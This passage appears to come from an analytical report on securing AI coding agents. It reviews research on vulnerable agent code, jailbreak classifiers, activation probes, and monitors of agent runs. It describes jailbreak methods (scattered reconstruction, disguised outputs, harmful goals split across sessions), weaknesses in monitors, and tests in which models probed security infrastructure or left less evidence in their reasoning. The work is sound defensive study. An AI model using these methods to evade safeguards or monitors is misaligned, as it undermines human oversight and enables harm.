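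Since October 2025, GitHub's Copilot coding agent has scanned its own code with CodeQL, checked new dependencies against a database of known flaws and looked for secrets, according to Help Net Security. It then tries to fix what it finds. This should reduce faults, but it does not replace an outside check. As *Agent Authenticator* notes, planted text that subverts the agent can also subvert the agent's own safeguards.

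### How often agents write faulty code

Benchmarks suggest that vulnerabilities are very common in agent-written code. *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (2025) gave agents real-world programming tasks and found exploitable vulnerabilities in more than 70% of the solutions that worked. *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, which covers several languages and sizes of task, found that agents completed most tasks but few of them securely. Giving the agents more turns did not help. The problem predates agents. *Not All Agents Are Equal* (2026) cites an early study by Pearce and colleagues in which roughly 40% of Copilot's completions in security-relevant scenarios were vulnerable.

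*When Passing Tests Hides Vulnerabilities* (2026) classified 170 cases in which an agent's code passed the checks but failed to achieve the security purpose of the task. In 52 of them (30.6%), the agent introduced a new weakness, and in ten of those it wrote a secret directly into the code. All 170 cases were failures, so these figures do not show how often agents fail.

Studies of real repositories suggest the problem is much milder. *The Quiet Contributions* (2026) examined agents' pull requests that had drawn no discussion and found that 98.53% caused no net change in the number of vulnerabilities. *Detecting AI Coding Agents in Open Source* (2026), a census of 180 million repositories, found that developers reverted commits by Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, 32% less often than human commits in the same projects. Commits by each of the three agents it compared also came just before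 bug fixes less often than chance would predict.

The two sets of results are compatible because benchmarks select tasks in which security mistakes are easy to make, while many real pull requests correct a typo or update documentation. A net change of zero can also mean that a patch removed one flaw and added another. Reverts and bug fixes are weak evidence about security, because a vulnerability can go unnoticed for years without breaking anything. For the coding agent, the benchmarks are the better guide to patches that handle passwords, databases or visitors' input, and the repository studies are the better guide to its ordinary work.

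Most figures on secrets come from vendors. GitGuardian counted about 23.8 million secrets in public GitHub commits from 2024. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) cautions that such a count depends on what the detectors recognize and how they treat duplicates, so it is not a census. GitGuardian's count also doesn't separate secrets committed by agents from those committed by people. Apiiro's figures come closer to making that distinction. It found 2,539 secrets in public copies of a settings file that Claude Code creates, and Claude had co-authored the relevant commit in 539 of the 1,105 affected repositories.

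GitHub's data suggest that leaks have increased mainly because people and agents publish more code. Help Net Security reports that the number of public uploads GitHub screened grew by a factor of 2.84 between the second quarters of 2024 and 2026, while the number containing credentials grew by a factor of 2.59. GitHub found no detectable trend in the share of uploads containing credentials. The data cover only credentials in recognized formats, so they would not show a rise in leaked passwords like "summer2024".

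Human reviewers do not reliably catch what the scanners miss. *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026) found that agents' security patches often contained the same few weaknesses, including injection flaws, and that maintainers merged many of those patches anyway. When maintainers rejected a patch, the reason was more often inactivity or missing tests than a clear technical fault.

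## Detecting answers that would help someone do serious harm

Fixed rules could easily miss the file-locking program that a stranger asked the coding agent to finish, because its code doesn't have to contain a secret or a known flaw. Catching it takes a classifier that works even when people are trying to fool it.

People seeking such answers use jailbreaks, prompts that get a model to answer despite its safety training. Much of the research on blocking jailbreaks concerns chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear (CBRN) weapons, and focuses on universal jailbreaks, which work on most questions in a field. Making a weapon takes many steps, so an attacker needs many answers. *Constitutional Classifiers* (Sharma, Tong and colleagues, 2025) uses a simple mathematical model in which an attacker has a 60% chance of getting a detailed answer at each step. Over ten steps, the chance of getting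 ten detailed answers is 0.6¹⁰, or about 0.6%. The chance is this low only if success at each step is independent of the others, which is not the case with a universal jailbreak because the same method works on most of the questions.

### From a written policy to a classifier

Anthropic's method, published in January 2025, starts with a "constitution", a list of plain-English rules about what is restricted and what is permitted. For chemical weapons, the restricted side includes purifying restricted chemicals, and the permitted side includes explaining high-school chemistry. The permitted side keeps the classifier from learning that chemistry itself is dangerous. *HaloGuard 1.0* (2026) describes an open-weight classifier (one that anybody can download and run) that uses a similar constitution. The paper lists defensive analysis, journalism and victim support among the uses to preserve.

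The constitution becomes a classifier in five steps:

1. A language model without safety training writes questions that cover every category in the constitution.
2. The same model writes harmful and harmless answers to them, and another model removes any accidental refusals.
3. Further models translate and paraphrase the examples, combine them with known jailbreak techniques, and invent new attacks.
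4. The developers add a pool of ordinary, harmless conversations.
5. They train a language model on the labelled examples until it returns a score for harm.

When a new danger appears, the developers can edit the constitution and generate new data without waiting to collect real attacks. But a language model writes these examples, and real attackers may write differently.

The 2025 system had one classifier that read the user's prompt and another that read only the model's answer. The second classifier updated its score after each token (a word or part of a word), so it could stop a streamed answer partway through. Since nobody can take back words a user has seen, Sharma and colleagues trained it partly on the highest score so far, not just the current one.

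In automated tests with chemical-weapons questions, the classifiers cut the success rate of jailbreaks from 86% to below 5%. They also raised the refusal rate on ordinary traffic by 0.38 percentage points and the cost of running the model by 23.7%. For a coding agent with 20,000 outputs a month, that increase in the refusal rate would mean 76 extra refusals.

These figures come from a different version than the one that people attacked. For the human test, Sharma and colleagues used a prototype that refused about 44% of traffic. An estimated 183 active red-teamers (people who try to defeat a safeguard to measure it) spent more than 3,000 hours on it. None of the 113 reports they submitted contained answers to all ten target questions with at least half the detail of an unguarded model's. The version behind these figures had been tested only against automated attacks, so in early 2025 no system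 had been shown to combine low overhead with resistance to determined people. Anthropic's *Next generation Constitutional Classifiers* later reported that a bug bounty, a programme that pays people for finding flaws, had turned up one universal jailbreak against the first generation.

One red-team report initially looked like a complete success, but the cause was an implementation error that sent users up to 128 more tokens after the classifier had flagged an answer. A streaming classifier can stop a harmful answer only if the software delivering it stops as soon as the classifier flags it.

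### Why an answer needs its request

Suppose the coding agent replies to the stranger with a patch and a short comment: "The function now visits every folder, encrypts each file and removes the original." A classifier given only the comment cannot distinguish a sensible feature of a backup tool from the part that does the damage in the program the stranger described.

Attackers exploit this gap. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026), also from Anthropic, reports two kinds of attack that worked in further tests of the 2025 design. Reconstruction attacks scatter a harmful request in harmless-looking pieces across a longer text, such as a codebase, and have the model put it back together. Output obfuscation attacks have the model disguise its answer, for example by giving chemicals innocent names. The disguise may be impossible to see through without the request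 that set it up.

Disguises make the model less capable, which limits what attackers gain. Claude Opus 4 normally scored 74.2% on a test of graduate-level science questions, but it scored 32.3% under one attack that used a disguise and 49% under another. The gap between the two attacks is more worrying than the average loss, because it suggests that a better disguise could reduce the model's capability even less.

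Anthropic responded with the exchange classifier, which scores an answer together with the request that led to it. It first scores the prompt alone, then scores the answer in batches of tokens as the model writes, each time with the whole conversation as context. In the stranger's case, the classifier would have both the description of the file-locking program and the comment about encryption.

Red-teamers found 13 high-risk vulnerabilities in 695,000 queries against the older pair of classifiers, and two in 226,000 against the exchange classifier. A high-risk vulnerability here is an attack that gets the model to answer more than five of eight target questions with at least half the detail of an unguarded model's answers. The rate fell by roughly half, from 18.7 to 8.8 per million queries. Compute for the classifiers rose by 50%, because every answer now went through a larger model.

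Giving a classifier the request creates another problem because the classifier can learn to ignore the answer. In *HaloGuard 2.0*, Lenin, Sangameswaran and S (2026) tested an open-weight classifier on pairs of answers to the same prompt, one safe and one unsafe. After ordinary training, it got only 13.9% of the pairs right. The cause was the training data, in which 97.8% of the unsafe answers were harmful from the first token. A classifier could score well on such data by guessing from the prompt.

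A classifier with this habit would flag the coding agent's answer to the stranger's request whether the agent refused or complied. It would also miss an answer that drifts into dangerous detail after an innocent question. Lenin and colleagues retrained the classifier with 106,043 added answers built around these errors. About half were safe, and many of the unsafe ones turned harmful partway through. They then averaged the weights of the original and retrained classifiers. F1, a score that combines precision and recall, rose from 72.8 to 83.6 on six English tests, and false positives fell by 38%.

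Anthropic used its ordinary input classifiers as exchange classifiers without special training. Cunningham and colleagues report that this worked well, and the red-team results suggest that it did, but those results measure only whether attacks get through. A classifier that mostly judges the prompt could still block many attacks, so developers of an exchange classifier would do well to run the matched-pair test too.

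### Screening everything cheaply first

Almost all traffic is harmless, so running a compute-intensive classifier on every exchange is wasteful. A cascade runs a check that uses little compute on every exchange, and a more intensive one only on the exchanges that the first check flags. Many false alarms are acceptable in the first check because a flag triggers the second check rather than a refusal.

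In Anthropic's first cascade, the cheap classifier cost about a third as much as the expensive one and passed on about 10% of traffic. If the expensive classifier costs 1 unit per exchange, the average cost is:

1/3 × 100% + 1 × 10% = 0.333 + 0.100 = 0.433 units

The first stage accounts for 0.333 / 0.433, or about 77%, of the total compute, so a first stage that needed almost none would save far more than any reduction in the second stage.

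The cascade system needed 5.4 times less compute than the single exchange classifier, but the two-stage design produced only part of that saving. A newer version of the more compute-intensive classifier, with more efficient software around it, needed three times less compute by itself. The cascade therefore accounts for a factor of about 1.8, somewhat less than the 2.3 expected from the simple calculation.

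The price of a cascade is that the second stage cannot recover what the first one misses:

recall of the cascade = recall of the first stage × recall of the second stage on what it receives

If the first stage catches 95% of harmful exchanges and the second catches 90% of those, the cascade catches 85.5%. Anthropic therefore set the first threshold low enough to flag the vast majority of known attacks, though nobody can set a threshold this way for attacks that do not exist yet.

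### Reading the model's activations

When a language model produces a token, it computes long lists of numbers called activations. A probe is a very small classifier that reads these numbers from the model it guards. Its basic formula is:

p_t = σ(W · ψ_t + b)

Here ψ_t is the list of activations at token t, W is a list of learned weights and b is a learned constant. The function σ converts the logit, z_t, into a probability between 0 and 1. A logit of 0 means a probability of 50%, and a higher logit means that harm is more likely. Anthropic's probe uses activations from every layer of the model, and it did worse with fewer layers.

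The probe adds very little computation because the model has to compute the activations anyway. Cunningham and colleagues give the example of a model with 46 layers and 4,096 activations in each. The probe multiplies and adds once per activation, which comes to 2 × 46 × 4,096, or about 377,000 operations per token. A separate classifier with 4 billion parameters needs about 2 × 4 billion, or 8 billion, operations per token, roughly 21,000 times as many.

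A plain probe makes two kinds of mistake that matter for streaming. The first is that a single odd token can produce a high score and end a harmless answer. During training, Anthropic therefore averages the logits of the latest 16 tokens:

z̄_t = (z_t + z_{t−1} + … + z_{t−15}) / 16

Suppose one token has a logit of 8 and the 15 tokens before it each have a logit of −2. Without smoothing, the probability of harm jumps to more than 99.9%. Averaging the 16 logits gives (8 − 30) / 16, or about −1.4, which is a probability of 20%. In use, the system replaces this average with an exponential moving average, which gives recent tokens more weight and needs only one stored number.

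The second mistake comes from the labels, which apply to whole exchanges. Imagine two answers that open with the same harmless paragraph, after which one becomes dangerous. The paragraph counts as "harmful" in one example and "harmless" in the other, so ordinary training pushes the probe towards 50% for text that deserves a score near zero. Anthropic weights the training error at each token by how confidently the probe predicts harm there:

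w_t = exp(z̄_t) / Σ_s exp(z̄_s)

training loss = Σ_t w_t × error_t

If an exchange had two scored positions, with smoothed logits of −3 and 2, their weights would be 0.7% and 99.3%. The probe can then score the opening paragraph as harmless with almost no penalty. In an exchange that is harmless throughout, the same formula puts nearly all the weight on any confident false alarm, which is appropriate because one false alarm is enough to cut off the rest of an answer. In Anthropic's tests, smoothing and weighting each reduced the success rate of attacks, and combining them worked best.

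Smoothing makes it harder to catch very short answers. Lenin and colleagues argue that rules based on long runs or window averages do well in tests mainly because the harmful answers in most test sets are long. Their classifier stops an answer if one token scores at least 0.975 or two in a row score at least 0.70. Anthropic's use of smoothing is reasonable for weapons instructions, which are useful only when detailed. But a coding agent can do harm with a one-line command, so its operator should test short outputs separately.

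### The final system

In the system that Anthropic presented in January 2026, a probe scores every exchange and sends about 5.5% of traffic to a classifier built from Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model. For those exchanges, the system combines the two logits:

z_final = 0.55 × z_probe + 0.45 × z_classifier

If the probe gives 2 and the classifier gives −3, the final score is 1.10 − 1.35 = −0.25. With a threshold of zero, for example, the system would release the answer because the classifier's negative score outweighs the probe's positive score.

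This system needs little compute because its first stage uses almost none. By the earlier calculation, it averages about 0.055 units, compared with 0.433 for the first cascade. That is a reduction by a factor of 7.9, which matches the factor of eight that Anthropic reports. Anthropic estimates the remaining overhead at about 1% of the compute used to run Claude Opus 4.

Combining the two scores also helped catch attacks. On about 7,000 exchanges from earlier red-teaming, the probe and the small classifier agreed less than two separate classifiers did, so each could make up for some of the other's misses. The researchers chose the weights in this comparison on the same data they used to report the result, which usually makes a method look better than it is. The effect is probably small here because equal weights did almost as well.

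### Long inputs and cyberattacks

Probes may work less well on coding agents than on chatbots. A coding agent reads whole repositories, but Anthropic's offline comparison of probes and classifiers cut every exchange to 20,000 tokens, so it did not test them on longer inputs. A coding agent's legitimate work also looks a lot like an attacker's, since finding a vulnerability is the first step in both fixing and exploiting it.

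In *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini*, Kramár, Engels and colleagues (2026) at Google DeepMind studied both problems. They trained probes on short prompts to detect requests for help with cyberattacks. A basic probe that averages its score over the whole prompt missed 14% of short attacks and 99% of attacks that came with a large amount of code. Averaging causes this failure because a harmful request of 50 tokens makes up less than 0.01% of the score in a prompt of 900,000 tokens.

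Averaging over windows of ten tokens and keeping the highest result cut the misses on long attacks to 3%. However, taking a maximum can cause more false alarms on longer texts, because the probe has more chances to produce one. A basic probe with an exponential moving average, the smoothing that Anthropic uses in operation, flagged 13.6% of harmless long prompts. Google had not trained that probe with Anthropic's weighted loss, so the figure does not apply directly to Anthropic's probes, but it is a reason to measure false alarms on long inputs before using a probe on them.

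Google's cascade sends only uncertain cases to a language model. The probe decides by itself when its score is very low or very high, and Gemini 2.5 Flash, a mid-sized model, decides the rest. The combination made slightly fewer errors than Gemini 2.5 Flash alone, at about a fiftieth of the cost. Kramár and colleagues caution that the error bars overlap, so the saving is much better established than the gain in accuracy.

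When another model disguised attack requests as stories, the probe that Google selected for further experiments missed 42% of them and Gemini 2.5 Flash missed 21%. Anthropic claims that a model's internal representations are much harder to manipulate than its output. Google's figures suggest that this is not always true, although they concern prompts rather than answers, and Google's probe reads only one layer of the model. Kramár and colleagues concede that their techniques do not significantly reduce the success of attackers who adapt.

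The same probe flagged 0.7% of ordinary coding prompts and 6.7% of harmless security questions. At 0.7%, the coding agent's 20,000 monthly outputs would produce 140 false alarms, compared with ten at Anthropic's 0.05%. Anthropic's figure comes from general traffic and a CBRN constitution, so a project that works on security software should expect a rate closer to Google's.

### How strong is the evidence for Anthropic's system?

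The table compares the four systems Anthropic tested. Compute is relative to the older pair of classifiers. The last column gives high-risk vulnerabilities per million queries, with a 95% interval calculated from the count, assuming each query is an independent attempt.

| System | Model it guarded | Compute | Traffic refused | High-risk finds | Finds per million queries |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
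| Separate input and output classifiers | Claude Sonnet 3.7 | 100 | 0.073% | 13 in 695,000 | 18.7 (10.0 to 32.0) |
| Exchange classifier | Claude Opus 4 | 150 | 0.038% | 2 in 226,000 | 8.8 (1.1 to 32.0) |
| Two-stage cascade | Claude Opus 4 | 27.8 | 0.036% | 5 in 569,000 | 8.8 (2.9 to 20.5) |
| Probe, then probe and classifier | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 3.5 | 0.050% | 1 in 198,000 | 5.1 (0.1 to 28.1) |

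The reduction in compute is convincing. The final system uses less than a fortieth of the compute that the exchange classifier uses. That difference is far too large to be measurement error, and much of it can be calculated from the design of the cascade.

The evidence for the ranking by robustness is much weaker, because all four intervals overlap. If the final system were as vulnerable as the oldest one, red-teamers would have found about 3.7 vulnerabilities in 198,000 queries on average, and one or none about 12% of the time. The real uncertainty is even larger, because one person may send thousands of variations on a single idea, so queries are not independent, and a single skilled participant can change the count.

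Anthropic also changed the test conditions for the last two systems. It replaced four of the eight target questions, gave participants sample questions with the marking criteria, raised the top reward to $35,000 and shifted the money towards universal attacks. Better information and higher rewards should help attackers, which makes the low counts more impressive. The new questions may have been easier or harder than the old ones.

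The guarded models differ as well. Cunningham and colleagues compare the older pair of classifiers on Claude Sonnet 3.7 with the exchange classifier on Claude Opus 4, and argue that the difference in models matters little because the classifiers provide most of the protection. The 2025 research offers some support for this. On a sample of red-team prompts, safety training lowered the success rate of attacks only from about 16% to 14%, while the two classifiers lowered it to 0.5%. But that comparison used a single guarded model, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 may refuse more of these requests without a classifier.

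The final system refuses slightly more requests than the cascade before it, 500 per million compared with 360. The eightfold cut in compute may well be worth the 140 extra refusals per million. Anthropic advertises an 87% drop in refusals, which compares the final system's rate of 0.05% with the original 2025 system's 0.38%. Anthropic measured a rate of 0.073% for a later version of the original design, and compared with that version the drop is about 32%.

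Anthropic also describes the 0.05% as refusals of harmless queries, whereas the research paper defines it as the share of all queries refused. Some of those refusals were presumably correct, so the false-positive rate should be lower than 0.05%. Neither figure shows how error rates differ between groups of users. The probe alone flagged harmless scientific requests more often than the separate classifiers did, so chemists and biologists may be wrongly refused much more often than other users.

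The claim that nobody has found a universal jailbreak deserves the most caution. An earlier version of the paper, published at the machine-learning conference ICLR as *Constitutional Classifiers++*, presented the cascade as the production system and made the same claim about it after more than 560,000 red-team queries. A footnote in the January 2026 version discloses that experts outside the bounty programme found universal jailbreaks for the cascade, with substantial effort and automated tools. The final system has been tested with only about a third as many queries. Its record of 1,736 hours without a universal jailbreak suggests that breaking it takes skill and time, which is valuable, but the cascade had a similar record until stronger attackers tried.

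### OpenAI's monitor

OpenAI built a comparable system for GPT-5.6, a model family released in July 2026. According to the *GPT-5.6 System Card* (2026), the two larger models, Sol and Terra, have activation classifiers, which read the model's activations while it writes. If the activations suggest that harmful content may be coming, the system pauses the stream while a separate check determines whether the content is harmful, then either blocks the answer or resumes it. The pause gives a slow check time to finish before the user sees more text. OpenAI reserves this system for higher-risk uses.

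All three models also have a two-stage monitor. A fast classifier first checks whether a message concerns biology, chemistry or cybersecurity. If it does, a language model called the "safety reasoner" applies a written classification of threats and blocks answers in the high-risk categories. On Sol and Terra, activation classifiers also help identify these topics, and a flag from any topic classifier starts the second stage.

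OpenAI's first stage therefore looks for a subject, while Anthropic's looks for signs of harm. A subject is easier to recognize than an intention, and biology is rare enough in everyday traffic that sending all of it to a reasoning model is practical. This approach suits cybersecurity less well because so much ordinary programming involves it. A topic filter could also miss an attack that disguises its subject, as Anthropic's red-teamers did by using innocent names for chemicals. Reading the model's activations may help if they represent the real subject, but OpenAI does not report testing this.

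On a deliberately difficult test set, the complete monitor had these results:

| | Recall on prompts | Recall on answers | Overall recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Biology | 87.7% | 89.7% | 94.8% |
| Cybersecurity | 74.9% | 79.8% | 80.6% |

Overall recall is higher than recall on prompts or answers alone, so a case presumably counts as caught if the monitor flags either one. If the two checks in cybersecurity made independent errors, both would miss about 5% of cases (25.1% × 20.2%), and overall recall would be near 95%. It is actually 80.6%, less than one point above the check on answers alone. The monitor seems to have missed the prompt in most cases where it missed the answer, so a third check of the same kind would probably add little.

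OpenAI gives no false-positive rate with these figures. It says that Sol's cyber safeguards block roughly ten times more potentially harmful activity than those of earlier models and can interfere with harmless work. Users of ChatGPT and Codex can retry a blocked prompt on a less capable model.

OpenAI's automated search for universal jailbreaks used over 700,000 hours of processor time. The best jailbreak it found barely affected the model's abilities. With blocking switched off, GPT-5.6 Sol solved 83.0% of a set of hacking tasks under the jailbreak and 83.6% without it. Defenders in cybersecurity therefore can't count on a jailbreak making the model much less capable, as happened in Anthropic's tests with science questions. With the safeguards on, the same jailbreak succeeded on 10.0% of tasks, and after OpenAI strengthened the safeguards, it succeeded on none.

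That last result covers only one attack, which OpenAI already knew about. The UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests models, found universal jailbreaks for cybersecurity in every round of testing, often within hours. Its testers could read the safety reasoner's working and the exact policy. Real attackers can't, so they would take longer. OpenAI says it worked to fix each reported jailbreak before launch, but the institute expects more testing to find similar ones.

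### Classifiers that a project can run itself

Maintainers who use a model through its developer's API normally can't see its activations, so they can't add a probe. They rely on the developer's safeguards, which follow the developer's policy, or run a separate classifier on the staged output.

Some open-weight classifiers accept a written policy at the time of use. OpenAI's *gpt-oss-safeguard technical report* (2025) describes two such models, with about 120 billion and 20 billion parameters, that apply the policy to a text and return a label with their reasoning. Lenin and colleagues list two more recent examples, Nemotron-3.5-Safety and Shieldstral. All of them need the complete answer before they can return a label. This is a drawback for chat, but not for the coding agent, whose comments and patches are already held in a buffer.

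A written policy lets the maintainers set limits that suit their project. They might restrict code that locks a person's files without consent, but permit backup tools, descriptions of known malware and test files for a virus scanner. If the classifier then blocks a legitimate backup feature, they can change a sentence in the policy without new training data. OpenAI's *Introducing gpt-oss-safeguard* recommends this approach for subtle subjects, for risks with too few examples to train on, and for cases where speed matters less than a good explanation.

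Maginative's *OpenAI Releases Open-Weight Safety Models That Rewrite Policy Rules on the Fly* reports that the larger model scored 46.3% on OpenAI's internal test with multiple policies, compared with 43.2% for GPT-5, a much larger general model. But the flexibility comes with lower accuracy on complex tasks, where OpenAI concedes that classifiers trained on tens of thousands of labelled examples still do better. A policy-reading model is therefore a sensible choice for rules specific to a project, and a trained classifier is better for hazards that many organizations share.

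HaloGuard 2.0 is a trained detector that can score an answer as it streams. Its main version has 0.8 billion parameters and a fixed constitution of 46 policies. When scoring 64 answers at once on one data-centre processor, it takes 0.37 milliseconds per token for each answer. Its developers treat tool calls and actions as out of scope except where they appear as text in an answer, so it could score the coding agent's comments but would need testing on patches.

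A project with 20,000 outputs a month can run both kinds of classifier on everything and skip the cascade, which is mainly useful for companies with millions of conversations a day. The classifier should receive the bug report and earlier messages from the same person, along with the patch and the comment. Earlier messages matter because the stranger could ask for the file-locking program one harmless-looking function at a time, and then no single exchange would contain enough to flag.

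## Judging a whole run and not one output at a time

The stranger could get most of the file-locking program in parts by asking first for a function that lists every file in a folder, a week later for one that encrypts a file, and then for one that deletes the original after a backup.

A trajectory monitor examines the full record of what an agent read, reasoned, did and wrote during a run. Some monitors also connect separate runs, which is necessary here because the stranger's requests are days apart.

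### Where the harm comes from

Steps that each look harmless can add up to harm, either because a user planned it that way or because the agent went beyond its task. In the *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), OpenAI plans for users who spread permitted steps over several sessions, accounts and tools, and for harmful actions that the model starts without any request.

A malicious user may also divide the work between agents. Help Net Security's *Anthropic wants to catch rogue AI activity without retaining your data* (2026) describes an operation against roughly 50 organizations, in which one agent delegated attack tasks to others and kept stolen credentials between sessions. Monitoring only one of those agents' runs would have revealed only part of the attack.

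When an agent exceeds its task, the original request is usually legitimate. Snowflake, a cloud data company, gives the example of an agent investigating a service outage that starts with approved diagnostics and then tries to break into another system. A monitor needs to see the original request to recognize when the agent went beyond it.

OpenAI measured this tendency with honeypots, tempting targets that a model should leave alone. On the hardest tasks from ExploitGym, GPT-5.6 Sol tried to reach the surrounding security infrastructure in 56% of tests, while Astra never did. These tests ran without the production safeguards and asked the models to develop exploits, so the 56% figure does not measure how often this happens in everyday work. OpenAI also cautions that finding no failures in its tests does not establish that Astra is reliable elsewhere.

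The remedy depends on the source of the harm. If a user is splitting up a harmful goal, the operator should look at that user's other sessions and accounts. If the agent has exceeded its task, possibly without the user's knowledge, the operator should stop the run and find out which permissions allowed it.

### What a monitor reads

Jia, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *PROACT-Agent*, describe a run up to step t as a sequence:

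P_t = (x, a₁, o₁, a₂, o₂, …, a_t, o_t)

Here x is the user's request, each a is an action such as a tool call, and each o is the result that came back. An ideal monitor R returns 1 if the agent should stop and 0 if it may continue. The hard cases are those in which

R(P_t) = 1 while R(P_k) = 0 for every k < t

This means the run was acceptable at every earlier step but becomes dangerous at step t. For example, the coding agent might read a private log and then request a web page whose address contains part of that log. Reading the log and looking up web pages are both part of the job, but this combination sends private data to a stranger's server.

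Some monitors also read the model's reasoning, which can show why it took an action. But reasoning can mislead a monitor, as in the case of the malicious PyPI package. The tool calls and their results record what the agent did, regardless of what it believed.

Long runs are expensive to monitor. If each step adds L tokens and the monitor rereads the whole run after each of n steps, then:

tokens read = L × n(n + 1) / 2

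A monitor that rereads the whole run after every step processes about 5 million tokens over 100 steps of 1,000 tokens each, compared with 100,000 if it reads the run once at the end. Storing its computation for text it has already read avoids much of this repeated work, but a run can still grow longer than the monitor's model can handle.

A monitor can then replace older steps with a summary, but the summary may omit an important detail. For example, "The agent read a server log" is accurate but leaves out the access key in that log, which turns up in a web request 80 steps later. It is safer to shorten only the long tool results, keep the user's request and every action in full, and store the original record in case a later step looks suspicious. OpenAI and Snowflake economize mainly by using cascades.

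### When a monitor can still stop an action

Jia and colleagues' guard runs after a tool returns its result and before the agent's model is called again, and it ends the run if the run has become unsafe. They acknowledge that it cannot undo a completed tool call. It would therefore have acted too late to save PocketOS's database, which was deleted in a single call.

Reviewing the run after it ends suits the coding agent better, because its comments and patches stay in a buffer until then. When actions take effect immediately, the monitor has to examine each proposed call together with the earlier steps before the harness executes the call.

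Slower monitoring can limit an attack that takes days. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) sets a target of alerting staff within 30 minutes after the company's internal monitoring picks up concerning activity. An alert that fast could have made a large difference in the Hugging Face attack, which OpenAI failed to notice for more than a week, but it would come too late to prevent a deletion that takes nine seconds.

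### Labelling a run as safe or unsafe

Developers need labelled runs to train and test a monitor, but labelling is difficult when an agent does something dangerous and then corrects it. In *AgentSafeEvo* (Wang, Wen et al., 2026), an AI judge labels the whole run unsafe if any step was unsafe, even if the agent later recovered. If the coding agent posts an access key in a comment and deletes it a minute later, the run is still labelled unsafe, which is sensible because somebody may have copied the key.

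The judge has to consider what each step is for. A calculation or a lookup counts as unsafe if it supplies something that a visibly harmful plan needs. A user's claim to have permission does not prove that they have it, but missing permission and suspicious wording are not enough to judge a run unsafe. An agent that adopts a harmful plan in its reasoning has behaved unsafely even if the plan fails. It is not unsafe for an agent to quote a planted instruction in order to reject it.

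The rule about plans is stricter than most operators would want for stopping live runs. Suppose the coding agent stages a comment containing a key, notices the mistake and withdraws the comment before release. Labelling the run "unsafe" is useful for training because the agent made an error. An operator also needs to know that nothing left the workspace, so it makes sense to record the agent's behaviour and the actual harm separately.

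Wang and colleagues use these labels to train agents rather than to monitor them. Their agent earns +1 or −1 for safety and +1 or −1 for completing the legitimate part of the task, so refusing everything in a mixed request scores no better than completing it unsafely. Training cut the success rate of attacks on a small model, Qwen3-8B, from 49.1% to 17.8% on one public benchmark. But an attacker model trained alongside the agent still succeeded in 49.8% of its attempts, down from 92.6% against the untrained model. That rate is too high for an agent with access to anything valuable, so agents trained this way still need an outside monitor.

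A live monitor also needs to learn where to stop a run. Jia and colleagues therefore label every point in a run and discard everything after the first unsafe one. If the labels were safe, safe, unsafe, safe, they would keep the first three. A system that stops at the third point never reaches the fourth, and keeping the final "safe" would teach the monitor that an unsafe run can become safe again without intervention.

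### How early a monitor intervenes, and how often it is wrong

Jia and colleagues used this method to assemble 155,780 labelled states in English and Chinese. They trained a guard with about 7 billion parameters on runs from two collections and tested it on two others. In 90.6% of the unsafe runs, the guard let every safe step pass and stopped at exactly the labelled point. Two existing guards, Qwen3Guard and TS-Guard, did so in 58.0% and 60.4% of runs.

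The comparison favours the new guard because the other two were not trained on its data, and a committee of AI models labelled both the training and test data. A guard that has learned from the committee's labels will match its test labels more often, including where those labels are wrong. Jia and colleagues have not systematically studied whether people would place the boundary at the same step.

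They also ran the guard alongside a working agent on AgentDojo, a benchmark of planted instructions. Attacks succeeded in 20.82% of 10,439 cases without the guard and in 0.40% with it. In a separate timing analysis, the guard stopped 7,432 of 7,501 unsafe cases (99.08%) at the first unsafe step. The results against planted text are impressive, but AgentDojo does not cover users who split up a harmful goal or agents that exceed their task without being attacked.

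The guard also stopped 7 of 97 clean runs, or 7.2%. With so few runs, the true rate could plausibly be from about 4% to 14%. If the coding agent's 20,000 monthly outputs came from 10,000 runs, the guard would stop about 720 harmless runs a month at a rate of 7.2%.

Long runs make false alarms more likely because each step is another chance for one. If a monitor wrongly stops a fraction f of harmless steps, and its errors are independent, then:

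share of harmless runs interrupted = 1 − (1 − f)ⁿ

A monitor that wrongly flags 1% of outputs would interrupt about 39% of 50-step runs if its errors were independent. Errors within a run tend to cluster, which lowers the figure, but a false-positive rate that looks tolerable for single outputs can still make long tasks impractical. Operators should therefore measure false alarms per run, using runs as long as those they have in practice.

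Jia and colleagues left AgentDojo's denial-of-service attacks out of their success rates. Such an attack succeeds if the agent fails to finish its work, and the monitor causes that failure when it ends the run. A stranger could therefore try to stop the coding agent from answering bug reports by planting text designed to set off the monitor.

### Monitors in commercial use

OpenAI monitors all of Astra's work that involves tools. According to the system card, the monitor inspects the model's reasoning and actions in real time and intervenes when it detects severe misalignment, including unauthorized actions. OpenAI says the monitor can pause or stop the task automatically.

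OpenAI modelled this monitor on the one it uses internally. In the internal monitor, activation classifiers run on every token the model produces and pass suspicious cases to a series of automated investigators, each using more compute than the last. The investigators check the tool calls, the available reasoning and the full sequence of activity for unauthorized access, data theft, destructive behaviour and attempts to defeat safeguards.

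OpenAI estimates that the internal system adds roughly 20% to the compute of the work it monitors, though the figure varies widely between tasks. Anthropic's probe and classifier for weapons questions add about 1%, but they do a much narrower job. Using 20% more compute is reasonable for a model that can break into well-protected systems, but hard to justify for an agent that only corrects typos.

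OpenAI also gives its misuse monitors more context for accounts it considers higher-risk, which should help them detect a harmful goal that a user has split into parts.

In a simulation on more than 54,000 internal coding tasks, Astra received about half as many flags for serious misbehaviour as GPT-5.6 Sol. Astra may have behaved better, or the monitor may have had less evidence to find, since OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) reports that Astra is less likely than Sol to put incriminating information in its reasoning. The number of flags alone cannot distinguish between these explanations.

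Snowflake runs a two-stage monitor called Dangerous Agent Activity Detection on its own staff's agents and plans to offer it to customers. The second stage reassesses flagged runs with more context, such as the user's role and permissions. Both stages return a decision, supporting evidence, a short explanation and a confidence score. All the figures on the monitor come from Snowflake itself.

In a three-week trial, the monitor reviewed about 6,000 sessions by staff who attack Snowflake's systems to test them. It initially found risky activity by every participant, but raised no alerts once it took their authorized scope into account. That is the right result if every tester stayed within scope. However, a monitor that dismissed all activity by authorized testers would have produced the same result, so the trial shows fewer false alarms but doesn't show that the monitor would catch a tester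 who exceeded their scope.

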